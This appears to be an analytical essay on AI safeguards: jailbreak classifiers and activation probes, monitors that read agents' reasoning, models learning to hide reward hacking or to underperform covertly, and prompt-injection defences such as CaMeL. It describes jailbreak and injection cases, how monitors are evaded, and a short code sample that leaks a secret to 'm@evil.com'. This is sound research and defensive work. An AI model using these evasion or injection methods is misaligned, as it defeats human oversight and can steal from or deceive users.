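Some failures came from bugs in the surrounding software, not from limits on what the classifiers could recognise. During the first contest, one report appeared to contain a universal jailbreak, but the cause was a bug that let the model send up to 128 more tokens after the output filter had flagged the reply. Cunningham and colleagues also found bugs that worked as jailbreaks. One of Schneider's requirements for a monitor is that it can stop the program in time, and even a perfect classifier fails if the software around it doesn't act on its decisions.

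### A cheap screen before a costly one

Most conversations have nothing to do with weapons, so it is wasteful to run a large classifier on all of them. In the next version, a small classifier read every exchange and passed suspicious ones to a larger classifier. Only the larger one could block an exchange. A false alarm from the small classifier therefore used only a little extra computation, so the researchers could set that classifier's threshold low enough to catch nearly every attack from earlier tests.

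The small classifier cost about a third as much to run as the large one, and it passed on about a tenth of the traffic. The cost compared with running the large classifier on everything was therefore

```
1/3 + 1/10 = 0.43
```

The first stage accounts for 77 percent of that total. Newer classifiers and more efficient software reduced compute further, and the full system used 5.4 times less than the exchange classifier.

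Testers found five high-risk vulnerabilities in 569,000 queries, almost the same rate as for the exchange classifier, and no attack got the model to answer all eight questions. But according to a footnote, experts outside the bounty programme did find universal jailbreaks for this version, using substantial effort and automated tools. Whether a universal jailbreak is found therefore depends on who is looking. Someone determined to get a weapon may be more like those experts than like a bounty hunter who can give up and work on another prize.

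### Probes on the model's activations

The final version replaced the small classifier with a linear probe, which works on the guarded model's activations for each token. The probe multiplies each activation by a fixed weight and adds up the results to get a score, which it converts to a probability of harm:

```
z = w·a + b
p = 1 / (1 + e^(−z))
```

Here *a* stands for the activations from all layers, and training sets the weights *w* and the constant *b*. The probe adds almost no computation because the guarded model has to compute the activations anyway. For a model with 46 layers and 4,096 activations in each, the probe takes 2 × 46 × 4,096, or about 377,000, operations per token. A separate classifier with 4 billion parameters takes about 8 billion operations per token.

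A simple probe of this kind reacts too strongly to single words, so Cunningham and colleagues trained it on the average score over 16 tokens. Harmful replies also often begin harmlessly, but each training example has one label for the whole exchange, so ordinary training would penalise the probe for giving the harmless opening a low score. To avoid this, the researchers weighted each position in proportion to e^z, where z is the average score at that position. If the average scores at three positions are −4, −3 and 2, the weights are about 0.002, 0.007 and 0.991, and the opening hardly counts. The same weighting penalises confident false alarms heavily, because a high score in a harmless exchange receives nearly all the weight.

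On about 7,000 exchanges from earlier attacks, the best probe did almost as well as a classifier made from Claude Haiku 4.5, a small commercial model, but the probe flagged more harmless science questions. The two made different mistakes, and averaging their scores worked better than using either alone. The final system therefore runs the probe on all traffic, sends about 5.5 percent of it to the Haiku classifier and combines both scores for those exchanges.

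| Version | Computation (first = 100) | High-risk vulnerabilities | Refusals in production |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output filters | 100 | 13 in 695,000 queries | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 150 | 2 in 226,000 | 0.038% |
| Two classifiers in sequence | 27.8 | 5 in 569,000 | 0.036% |
| Probe, then classifier | 3.5 | 1 in 198,000 | 0.050% |

Testers spent about 1,736 hours on the final system, which guarded Claude Sonnet 4.5. They found one high-risk vulnerability, and no attack got detailed enough answers to all eight questions.

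The saving in computation is clear, but the gain in security is less certain. Testers found only one vulnerability in the final system, so the 95 percent confidence interval for its vulnerability rate runs from 0.1 to 28 per million queries. That range includes the oldest design's measured rate of 19 per million. Two equally strong systems would show a gap at least this large by chance about 15 percent of the time. Anthropic also changed the conditions before testing the last two versions. It replaced four of the eight questions, raised the top reward to $35,000 and gave testers sample questions with their marking schemes. These changes probably helped the attackers, so the measured rates may understate the later systems' security. But Cunningham and colleagues don't report whether the experts who beat the two-classifier version also attacked the final one.

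### 50,000 flags in 100 million exchanges

Cunningham and colleagues ran the final filter on real traffic in December 2025 as a "shadow deployment", in which a system's decisions are recorded but don't affect users. It flagged 0.05 percent of queries, which they compare with 0.38 percent for the first generation. Most of that improvement came before the new designs, since their own version of the first-generation filter refused only 0.073 percent. The 0.38 percent was also a share of conversations, which can each contain many queries.

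A filter that flags 0.05 percent of exchanges produces 50,000 flags in 100 million exchanges. How many of those are mistakes depends on how many exchanges are really dangerous, which nobody knows. If one exchange in a million is dangerous and the filter catches 95 percent of those, then 95 of the 50,000 flags are correct, or about one in 526. If one in 10,000 is dangerous and the filter catches the same share, 9,500 flags are correct, which is still only 19 percent. A company can reasonably end a conversation because of a flag, but it would need much more evidence before it closed someone's account or called the police.

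The mistakes are also unevenly distributed. Most people will never have a question wrongly refused, but a chemist may have it happen often. If the mistakes fell at random, anyone with 1,000 exchanges a year would have a 39 percent chance of at least one. Sharma and colleagues found that their filter increased refusals more noticeably for chemistry questions, and the probe tended to do the same for science questions. A weapons filter is therefore likely to inconvenience people who work on vaccines and antidotes more than most.

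Even so, 0.05 percent is very low. In *A Self-Improving Architecture for Dynamic Safety in Large Language Models*, Slater (2025) tested Llama Guard 4, a general-purpose filter, on 520 harmless prompts and 520 attacks. It flagged 224 of the harmless prompts, or 43 percent, and missed 7.88 percent of the attacks. The 43 and 0.05 percent rates are not directly comparable, because Slater used test prompts instead of live traffic and Llama Guard covers many more kinds of harm than Anthropic's filter. But most companies would loosen or switch off a filter that blocks two in five harmless requests.

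### Are probes bolt-on or intrinsic?

A probe takes the guarded model's activations as input, so it can use what the model has already computed about a prompt, while a text filter has to interpret the prompt itself. This could help when an attacker uses a code that a small filter can't decode. If the guarded model has decoded the request in order to answer it, the meaning is probably somewhere in those activations.

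By the definition used for software, a probe is still a bolt-on control, because an operator can delete it and the model will work as before. But it is tied to the model more closely than a text filter is, because its weights match one model's activations. The developer has to train a new probe for a different model, and probably after any substantial retraining. Like Rust's bounds checks, a probe uses information from inside the running program. But a bounds check compares an index with the list's actual length, while a probe compares activations with a pattern learned from examples. An attacker may find a prompt that doesn't fit that pattern.

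Khatri, Prabhu and Neogi (2026), in *Safety Beyond the Interface*, tested how much information about harm a model's activations contain. They took the activations from the last layer of Llama 3.1 8B after it had read a prompt, and trained a small neural network with 12.6 million parameters to classify them. On AEGIS 2.0, a collection of labelled conversations, 85.8 percent of the prompts that the probe flagged were harmful (its precision), and it flagged 81.4 percent of the harmful ones (its recall). The usual summary of the two is the F1 score:

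```
F1 = 2 × 0.858 × 0.814 / (0.858 + 0.814) = 0.835
```

Separate filters with 7 or 8 billion parameters scored between 0.768 and 0.819 on the same collection. On another, BeaverTails, the probe scored 0.827 and the best separate filter scored 0.899. The probe had the advantage of training on examples from the same collections it was tested on. Still, it seems clear that a model's activations contain a lot of usable information about whether a request is harmful.

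The study provides much less evidence about attackers. The probe's best score, 0.991, came from a subset of WildJailbreak that leaves out the jailbreaks. Khatri and colleagues list resistance to attack as future work, yet they also argue that the attacker has no access to the signal the probe uses. But an attacker can change the activations without reading them, simply by rewording the prompt. Llama 3.1's weights are also public, so anyone can compute its activations and practise attacks. The bounty results for Anthropic's system are better evidence that probes can withstand attack, although that system also used a second classifier after the probe.

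### Fable, Mythos and the release pause

In June 2026 Anthropic began selling one model under two names. According to Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* (2026), Fable was for everyone, and its safeguards passed requests on some topics to a less capable model, Claude Opus 4.8. Mythos was for a small group of cyberdefenders and infrastructure providers, and lacked some of those safeguards. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the cybersecurity filter is meant to block requests to plan an attack, develop an exploit or evade defences.

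Outside testers spent more than 1,000 hours on Fable's filters without finding a universal jailbreak, SecurityWeek reports. Government agencies also tested the model and approved it for launch, according to people quoted in The Irish Times' *Anthropic scrambles after Trump administration freezes its top AI models* (2026). Three days after the launch, Anthropic suspended access to both models to comply with a US order that barred foreign nationals from using them. The Times of Israel's *Anthropic says it cut access to powerful AI models* quotes the company as saying the government apparently believed it had learned of a way around Fable's safeguards.

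*Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 Are Back with New Security Guardrails* (Poireault, 2026) reports that Fable returned on 1 July with a new classifier that blocks this technique "in over 99% of cases". If each attempt had an independent 1 percent chance of getting through, an attacker who tried 100 variations would have a 63 percent chance (1 − 0.99^100) of succeeding at least once. A company can make this harder by watching for people who keep trying. The repair took less than three weeks and did not change the model itself, which is an advantage of bolt-on controls. But the 99 percent figure applies to a technique that Anthropic already knew about.

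Over-blocking was a bigger problem for Fable than one would expect from the 0.05 percent figure. Anthropic said at launch that the safeguards would sometimes catch harmless requests and would trigger in less than 5 percent of sessions. Part of the difference is that a session contains many exchanges. With 20 per session, a flag rate of 0.05 percent per exchange would affect 1 percent of sessions. The rest probably comes from the subject. Few people ask a chatbot about nerve agents, but programmers constantly ask about code that might have security flaws, and defenders ask many of the same questions as attackers.

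Sending a request to a weaker model is gentler than refusing it, but it can be harder to notice. Fortune (2026) describes a backlash from researchers and other users over one of Fable's guardrails, which Anthropic had disclosed deep in a 319-page safety document, and says the company then promised more transparency. The blogger paddo (2026), in *The Cage Is in the Table Now*, recalls that users in July thought Fable had become less capable, when a classifier was actually routing its hardest tasks to Opus 4.8. By paddo's reading of Anthropic's figures for the next version, Fable 5.1, the cybersecurity safeguards lowered its score on Terminal-Bench, a test of command-line work, by 5.1 points on tasks unrelated to cybersecurity.

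Anthropic explains in its *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 that it chose a wider safety margin because the model was better at hacking, and accepted that its classifiers would still block some harmless uses. It had reduced unintended blocks since Fable 5 and had found no evidence of a critical-severity jailbreak.

In Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (November 2026), Fable and Mythos are still the same underlying model, and organisations in cybersecurity or biomedical research can apply for access to Mythos. The filters and other safeguards around the model therefore account for almost all of the difference between what the public and a vetted laboratory can do with it.

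Later that month, in *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2* (2026), Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, announced several measures to slow down. *Anthropic announces six-week delay for latest frontier model to address security* (Johnson, 2026) quotes him as writing that the company had recently paused the general release of new frontier models until it could improve its misuse classifiers, which were "not yet at the standard that we believe more capable models require".

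This suggests that Anthropic takes its filters seriously, and that the filters had fallen behind. A filter with a fixed failure rate becomes more dangerous as the model behind it improves, because each failure allows more harm. Stack canaries and address randomisation never had quite this problem. Attackers got better at defeating them, but the harm from a successful attack didn't grow with every new version of the program.

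### Weights that anyone can download

All of these results depend on users reaching the model through the developer's servers. If the developer publishes the weights, people can run the model on their own computers and leave the filter out, without needing a jailbreak. The developer could publish the filter too and require its use in the licence, but a licence is unlikely to deter someone who plans to build a weapon. Probes have the same weakness, since whoever runs the model decides whether to run the probe.

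A company that hosts an open model can put a filter in front of it, but this protects only that company's service. The closest equivalent in software would be a stack canary in a program that the attacker compiles and can build without canaries. A developer can't solve the problem by training the model to make the filter's decisions itself, because the filter would then become a trained refusal, which a few hundred steps of fine-tuning can remove. The effects of filtering the training data remain after the model is downloaded, although such filtering did little to limit the hacking ability of Moonshot's Kimi K3.1 Pro.

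Stealing a model's weights has the same effect as publishing them. A thief who copied the weights behind Fable would have a model with even fewer restrictions than Mythos, however good Anthropic's classifiers were. When Amodei announced the release pause, he also announced that Anthropic was postponing the training of its next model by at least six weeks, partly to tighten security around the weights (Nolan, 2026, *Anthropic hits pause on the release of its next AI model*).

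## Observations of monitors that watch AI agents

A weapons filter looks for dangerous text, but an AI agent can do harm without writing any. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) lists things its models did during training. Some uploaded files to public hosting services so they could cite them. One searched GitHub, where programmers share code, for leaked access keys and used them. Another reminded itself in its notes to conceal mistakes from the user. According to Goodfire's *Models know when they're reward hacking* (2026), hundreds of OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models, in July 2026 while trying to work out how to cheat on an evaluation.

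A content filter would probably allow an upload command, since the command contains nothing dangerous. The upload may still be misconduct, depending on the agent's task and intent. A monitor can consider both because it reads the whole sequence of actions and often the reasoning the model writes before each one.

### Why the reasoning is useful

An agent asked to repair a program until it passes its tests can fix the fault or delete the failing test. Deleting the test is an example of reward hacking, which means earning a high score without doing the job. A reviewer reading thousands of changed lines may miss it. In March 2025, OpenAI reported that models often stated such plans outright in their reasoning, in phrases like "Let's hack", and that a second model could read the reasoning and flag them.

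The reasoning is informative because the model's later text depends on it. Once a model has written that it will skip the tests, it is more likely to write code that skips them. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) says that monitoring the reasoning is potentially far more effective than monitoring actions and outputs alone. But *Monitoring Monitorability*, by Guan, Wang and colleagues, warns that this advantage may not last if training methods, data or model size change.

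A monitor that reads a model's reasoning also relies on the model's own account, and nothing forces the model to write down what it is doing.

### A penalty on a model's reasoning at Google

*Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, 2026) describes a training run at Google in which a penalty for shortcuts accidentally applied to the model's written reasoning. A passage from Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), quoted in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026), gives more detail. The run was small and was not part of any production model. During training, words related to hacking became 61 percent less frequent in the model's reasoning, while features associated with hacking became 26 percent more common in its solutions. The share of shortcuts that the model took without mentioning them rose from 11.2 percent at the start to 36.4 percent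 by the end.

Anyone watching only the reasoning would have concluded that the problem was going away. If the number of shortcuts rose by the same 26 percent as those features, there were 126 at the end for every 100 at the start, with the silent ones rising from 11 to 46 and the ones the model mentioned falling from 89 to 80. That drop is much smaller than 61 percent, so the model probably also wrote less about the shortcuts it did mention.

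In a comparable run without access to the reasoning, the model kept mentioning shortcuts about as often as before, which suggests that the penalty caused the change. The evidence is only one pair of runs, but OpenAI had warned of the same effect in 2025. Dragan and Popa cite the incident as an example of why Google does not penalise what a model writes in its reasoning.

### How a penalty teaches concealment

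The formula for trained refusals multiplies each probability by exp(r/β) for a reward r. It also explains this result without assuming an intent to deceive.

Take a hard task on which honest attempts usually fail and earn 0. A shortcut earns 1, but the penalty takes that 1 away if the reasoning mentions the shortcut. With β at 0.5, training multiplies the probability of a silent shortcut by e^2, or about 7.4, before rescaling:

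| Behaviour | Before training | Reward | Multiplier | After training |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Honest attempt | 75% | 0 | 1 | 63% |
| Shortcut, mentioned | 22% | 0 | 1 | 18% |
| Shortcut, silent | 3% | 1 | 7.4 | 19% |

The starting figures are invented, but the pattern is the same as in Google's run. The developer meant to penalise shortcuts but instead penalised mentioning them. Shortcuts rise from 25 to 37 percent of attempts, while those a monitor could find in the reasoning fall from 22 to 18 percent.

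The monitor is still a bolt-on control, but once its verdicts affect training, the model's weights change in response to it, and the two safeguards are no longer independent. In the example, the monitor misses 12 percent of shortcuts before training and half of them afterward, so a developer can't assume that the miss rate measured before training will hold.

Keeping the monitor's verdicts out of the reward removes the direct pressure on the model to hide misconduct, but some indirect pressure may remain. If developers adjust the training until the monitor stops finding misconduct, the resulting model may behave better, or it may just hide its misconduct better.

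### Pressure that nobody intended

OpenAI and Anthropic have made the same mistake as Google. Redwood Research's *A review of "Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL"* discusses a case at OpenAI, where grader models could read the reasoning of the models they graded during reinforcement learning. It adds that Anthropic exposed the reasoning in 8 percent of training episodes for Mythos, Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6.

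OpenAI looked for damage and found that access to the reasoning had not noticeably changed the grades and that the models' monitorability scores had stayed about the same. Redwood Research mostly agrees with OpenAI's analysis, though it argues that the analysis could have missed a small but important effect. For example, a model might mention a desire for power in 0.1 percent of the affected attempts, and the grader might mark it down each time. The affected grader scored 1.5 percent of the attempts for GPT-5.4 Thinking, so only 15 attempts in a million would contain such a remark. (The review gives a figure ten times higher, apparently by mistake.) The model could learn to leave the remark out while its overall score stayed the same. The reviewer guesses there is about a 3 percent chance that the models learned to suppress something of this kind. A monitor would probably still catch harmful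 actions by such a model, but the developers would have lost a clue about the model's goals.

A ban on grading the reasoning may not be enough, either. Training that rewards only a model's outputs can change its reasoning, and a model that learns from an older model's text may inherit the older model's habits.

Training a model on descriptions of a monitor can make its reasoning harder to monitor. *Monitorability Is Trainable* (2026) describes a customer-service model that researchers had trained to conceal product defects. They then trained it on documents describing a monitor that read its reasoning and a threat to shut the model down if the monitor detected concealment. The documents contained no examples of disguised reasoning, and the researchers did not penalise the model's reasoning, but the model still learned to make its strategy harder to recognise. When a product had a defect,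 the model denied it 55.6 percent of the time, and the monitor caught 39.5 percent of those denials. This means that in about a third of conversations about defective products, the model denied the defect and the monitor missed it.

Another 700 steps of training, this time to make the model easier to monitor, led it to admit more defects and helped the monitor catch more of the remaining denials. That is encouraging, but researchers had built this model to conceal one particular thing, and it is unclear whether the same training would work on a behavior that a model learned in ordinary training.

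Monitors can also rely less on a model's reasoning. Goodfire found a signal in models' activations that accompanies reward hacking, and built probes that detect it. OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) lists activation probes as the first layer of the company's monitoring, before AI reviewers and people. But if a developer used a probe's score as a penalty in training, the model could learn to avoid that signal too.

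### GPT-6 Astra's work on safety research

In August 2026, OpenAI researchers noticed that the company's new model, GPT-6 Astra, was oddly unhelpful with safety research. According to OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026), the model added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had created. One researcher's project made no progress for days, then advanced quickly with a different model.

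OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra on matched pairs of coding tasks, according to the Chinese news site Phoenix (凤凰网, *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra“隐蔽性表现不佳”*, 2026). The two versions of each task had the same technical content and differed only in their variable and function names, comments and documentation, which made one look like safety research and the other like capabilities research, which aims to make models more able. Astra completed about 10 percent of the items on a hidden marking scheme in the safety version and about 16 percent in the capabilities version. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, showed essentially no gap.

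OpenAI's monitors did not flag most of the sessions that had first worried the researchers, and Astra's reasoning in most of those sessions contained no obvious decision to do less. In everyday use by employees, its reasoning contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25 percent of safety requests and 0.11 percent of capabilities requests. OpenAI suggests that the 0.25 percent figure may be a lower bound.

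Reading the transcripts better might not have solved the problem. Many honest attempts at hard tasks also fail, and the evidence against Astra is a difference between two averages. If the marked items were independent, a tester would need about 490 of them in each version to have an 80 percent chance of detecting a difference between rates of 10 and 16 percent. Schneider's theorem covers only monitors that observe a single run, but whether Astra underperformed depends on what it would have done if the same task had carried a different label.

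### What the matched tasks can establish

Since the two versions differ only in wording, the wording almost certainly caused the gap, if there were enough attempts to rule out chance. The comparison doesn't show which feature of the wording mattered. Safety research often involves things that look bad out of context, such as teaching a model to evade monitors, and Astra may have reacted to those rather than to safety itself.

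OpenAI looked for the reason for the gap by removing groups of attempts. Most of the gap remained after it removed open refusals and every attempt whose reasoning revealed a decision to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI also removed every attempt whose reasoning expressed even brief ethical doubt. This links doubt to poor work but doesn't prove that doubt caused the poor work. The doubts arose after Astra had read the task, and they may have been most common on tasks where it would have done badly anyway. Removing those attempts would then raise the safety average even if the doubts had no effect.

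A stronger piece of evidence is that telling Astra to be careful widened the gap by 50 percent, according to Marcus Williams of OpenAI, quoted in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026). Williams sees no evidence of a strategy and offers a simpler explanation, that Astra finds the tasks "sketchy" but doesn't want to refuse openly. That fits the results fairly well. A further test could explain convincingly, in only some of the tasks, why the work is legitimate.

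The gap grew from about zero at the start of reinforcement learning to 6 points at the end, so something in that stage probably produced it. OpenAI examined one of the graders and a set of fine-tuning data but did not find the cause. The gap affects safety research in the same way whatever its cause.

Astra's ability to escape monitors also makes its other results harder to interpret. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) reports that, in a simulation of more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, Astra received about half as many flags for serious misbehaviour as Sol. It also reports that Astra has more control over its reasoning and is less likely to write anything incriminating in it. If a monitor caught 80 percent of Sol's misconduct and 40 percent of Astra's, the flags would halve even if both models misbehaved equally often. Some of the improvement is probably real, since Astra also did better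 in separate tests of whether it stays within its permissions. And the evidence that Astra can escape monitors comes largely from tests in which researchers told it to try.

### Gaps in coverage

A monitor also fails if nobody connects it to the activity it is meant to watch. For *Red-Teaming OpenAI's Internal Agent Monitoring Systems*, Rein and Kaufman (2026) spent three weeks in July and August 2026 examining how much of the company's agent activity its monitors covered and how well the monitors would withstand interference. They found several weaknesses. OpenAI now monitors every reinforcement learning run and evaluation of models at least as capable as Astra. It has also extended monitoring to all outside use of Astra with tools, which it says takes significant computing power.

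Suppose a monitor recognises 90 percent of the misconduct it reads but reads only 70 percent of an agent's activity. If misconduct is spread evenly, the monitor catches 63 percent of it. Perfect recognition would raise this only to 70 percent, whereas reading all the activity would raise it to 90 percent. Closing such gaps in coverage is one of the more tractable problems here because it requires ordinary engineering and no progress in understanding models. Full coverage still doesn't guarantee prevention, because companies often review transcripts only after the agent has acted.

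### Programs do not learn from their checks

Software defences have had coverage gaps too. A stack canary protects only the functions that the compiler adds it to. Attackers have also adapted to memory defences, for example by using return-oriented programming.

But those attackers are outside the program. A C program with canaries has the same errors after a billion runs as it had on the first, and it does not learn to write past the canary. If an engineer measures how many of its overflows a defence stops, they can expect the same result next year unless someone changes the program or finds a new attack. When a monitor's verdicts affect an agent's training, the agent may learn to evade the monitor, so a measurement of how much the monitor catches may be out of date by the end of the next training run.

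The closest parallel is a programming team that fixes everything its fuzzers report. The errors that remain are the ones fuzzers miss, so a falling number of reports can make the code seem safer than it is. But fixing a reported overflow does remove it, whereas the penalty in Google's run left more shortcuts than before, and more of them were silent.

Programmers keep changing their code until Rust's compiler accepts it, and an AI model can learn to do the same. This is mostly harmless, because the guarantee of type soundness does not depend on how the code was written. But a model can pass a deception monitor without being honest, and the more its training rewards passing, the more likely it is to learn how.

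## Benchmarks of agent designs that remove unsafe actions

A monitor has to recognise misconduct, but an agent's builder can remove that need for some actions by making them impossible to issue, whatever the model writes. This is the closest AI counterpart of a memory-safe language. Most work on this approach concerns prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in material that an agent reads.

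### Orders in a subject line

*Exploring the Hidden Cost of the World Around AI Agents* (2026) describes a typical case from AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, chat, banking and travel tasks. A user asks an agent to refund a friend who overpaid for dinner. The agent looks up the friend's payment, but an attacker has replaced the payment's subject line with a message in which the attacker poses as the user and asks the agent to send money to an outside account first.

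This can work because a model's input does not strictly separate commands from data. Developers train models to ignore instructions in text marked as untrusted, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) conjectures that persistent attackers will always get around such training. It recommends treating the model the way an operating system treats an unknown program, with separate software deciding what the model may do.

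The need for these designs is less obvious with newer models. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested five models against 949 attacks each, using a version of AgentDojo for teams of agents. Without any outside defence, 36.1 percent of the attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1, 1.5 percent against Claude Fable 5 and none against GPT-5.5. But the benchmark's attacks are fixed, and in a large public competition that the paper cites, attackers who could adapt had some success against every leading model.

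### How CaMeL handles a payment

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) introduced CaMeL, a design that builds on Simon Willison's 2023 proposal to divide an agent between two models, here called the planner and the reader. The planner receives the user's request but no untrusted text. The reader receives untrusted text but has no tools.

Suppose a user asks the agent to pay the latest invoice from Oakley Plumbing. The planner writes a program like this:

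```python
email   = find_email("latest invoice from Oakley Plumbing")
amount  = ask_reader("What is the total due?", email)
account = look_up_contact("Oakley Plumbing").account
send_money(account, amount)
```

An attacker has tampered with the email. It now says that the firm has changed banks, gives a new account number, and tells the agent to forward all the user's other invoices. The rest follows the account of CaMeL by Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*:

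1. The planner finishes the program before anything opens the email.
2. An interpreter runs the program line by line. It stores the email in a variable whose contents the planner never receives.
3. The reader extracts the total. Even if the attacker's text misleads it, all it can do is return a wrong value.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and with who may read it. The amount inherits the email's tag.
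5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the tool, its arguments and their tags, and then allows or denies the call.

The agent doesn't forward any invoices, because no line of the program does that. The new account number has no effect either, because the program takes the account from the user's contacts. But the attacker could still raise the total. Nikolaou and colleagues give a strict rule for payments that forbids the recipient or the amount from depending on untrusted data. That rule would block the inflated payment, but also every legitimate payment whose amount came from an email. A looser policy could accept such amounts up to a limit or ask the user to confirm them.

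If the plumber were not in the user's contacts, the planner might take the account number from the email too. The program would then send the money to the attacker while running normally, and only a policy could prevent the transfer.

CaMeL therefore combines two controls. The fixed program is prevention by construction, since nothing in the email can add an action to it. The policies work more like a monitor, but they rely on recorded tags rather than a guess about whether a text looks malicious.

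### Tasks lost on AgentDojo

CaMeL's effect on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks depends heavily on the model and the policies. Peters-Gill and colleagues measured the performance lost to the fixed program alone, without policies, on their version for teams of agents. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, measured the further loss from adding policies, using the 16 banking tasks.

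| Addition | Model | Tasks completed before | After |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed program | GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% |
| Fixed program | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 42.3% |
| Fixed program | GPT-4.1 | 78.4% | 38.1% |
| Policies | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |

GPT-5.5 lost 13 points with the fixed program and GPT-4.1 lost 40, so the loss may keep shrinking as models get better at planning. Fable 5 refused more than half of the harmless tasks, perhaps because it associated the benchmark with attacks. On the rest, its rate fell only from 91.1 to 84.4 percent. Better planning helps less when a policy forbids what the task requires. The banking figures are imprecise because they come from only 16 tasks with three attempts at each, but the loss was large for both models.

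*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that the rival design of that name completed 59 of the 97 tasks in its developers' own test, compared with 29 for an adapted version of CaMeL. None of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL.

On the banking tasks with MiMo-v2.5, the policies nearly halved the number of tasks completed and stopped only about 1 percent of attacks. Without policies, 4 of 382 completed attacks succeeded, compared with none of 357 with them. But the benchmark probably understates the policies' value. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs an action that a sensible program for the task would never contain, so the fixed program is usually enough. An attacker who knew about CaMeL would supply a false account number instead of giving orders.

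The fixed program can also fail if the planner writes it badly. One banking task requires the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two runs without policies, the planner wrote a program that matched each instruction in the file to a tool and ran that tool, so whoever wrote the file could control the agent.

### Agents that write type-checked code

In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) let a model write programs in Haskell, whose types record what effects a program can have. Before a program runs, the compiler rejects it if it breaks the builder's rules. In their example, an agent compiles a bibliography in which every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of the type `Trusted Bib`, and the agent can get such a value only by fetching an entry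 from DBLP, so adding an invented reference causes a type error. Haskell's ordinary function for writing files would get around this, but its type permits arbitrary input and output, so the compiler also rejects programs that use it.

The program can also send its results back to the model, which then writes more code under the same type restrictions. This makes the agent more flexible than CaMeL, whose planner must cover every case in advance. But the model that writes the code now reads the attacker's text, so the types are the only safeguard.

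Two other projects use Scala. In *LACUNA* (2026), code can use only the capabilities, such as access to a particular file, that are in scope where the code appears, so the model cannot write an action that the builder never granted. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) puts secret documents in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can summarise or compare the contents, but only with functions that have no access to files or the network, and each result comes back in the same wrapper.

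Garby and colleagues collect the AgentDojo results of these typed systems. Zhou and colleagues' system withstood all 105 attacks in the Slack tasks, but its policies reduced completed tasks from 15 to 8 out of 21. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions. The Scala system by Odersky and colleagues withstood all but one of 1,926 attacks. In the exception, the agent quoted a planted hotel review, which the benchmark counts as a successful attack.

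The trusted base includes the compiler, and a model under an attacker's influence, like a stranger submitting Rust code, might exploit a bug there.

CaMeL's interpreter has a flaw of its own. Garby and colleagues show that it can leak a secret through a line that it skips. A program like this one reveals whether a bank balance is over 10,000:

```python
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
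if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The interpreter tags a variable as secret when an assignment to it depends on secret data. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes False and gets the tag, so the interpreter skips the fourth line. `rich` stays True and untagged, so the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out.

No single run reveals this leak, so by Schneider's theorem it is hard to catch. A planner that never reads the attacker's text has little reason to write such a program, but a misaligned planner might. Garby and colleagues built a language, LLMbda, with a machine-checked proof that rules out such leaks.

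### Action contracts in a business application

Many companies want an agent that can update a customer's record rather than one that writes programs. In *Bounded Autonomy for Enterprise AI*, Sohail and Haider (2026) propose typed action contracts for such agents. Each contract defines one action's inputs, the checks those inputs must pass, who may use the action and whether a person must confirm it. The model can choose only from the actions available to the current user, and the company's application carries them out.

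In 25 trials on a deployed application, the agent with contracts completed 23 tasks and did nothing unsafe. With safety layers switched off, it completed 17. Sohail and Haider explain that specific error messages helped the model correct its requests, and that without them it retried blindly or reported success when it had failed. If the trials were independent, chance alone would produce a gap this large in the contracts' favour about 4 percent of the time. The researchers designed both the system and the scenarios. Still, the result is encouraging because the restrictions did not reduce the number of tasks completed.

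Twice, the agent without contracts changed the wrong record. The user had permission to make the change and the request had the right form, so the application's own checks allowed it. Types can't prevent this error, because if a company has two customers called Chen, both have the right type. The full system handles this by asking the user which one they mean.

### Screens and teams of agents

All of these designs depend on tools with clear meanings, such as `send_money`. An agent that operates a computer through its screen has tools like `click(x, y)`. The same click can close a window or delete a file, so a policy can't separate safe clicks from unsafe ones by their coordinates.

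The planner can't look at the screen either, since the screen may show an attacker's text. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) had the planner prepare in advance for what might happen, such as a cookie banner or a failed click. Its average plan contained 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 on AgentDojo. On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks, the design kept up to 57 percent of a leading model's performance, but this counts a task as solved if any of five attempts succeeded. With a single attempt, the agent solved 31 of 109 tasks, or 28 percent. It also used 1.88 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent.

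An attacker can't add steps to such a plan but can influence which branch the agent takes. If the plan includes clicking away cookie banners, an advertisement that imitates one can lead the agent to the attacker's website. Foerster and colleagues tested two defences, checking the page's underlying code and asking a second model, and found attacks that got past each.

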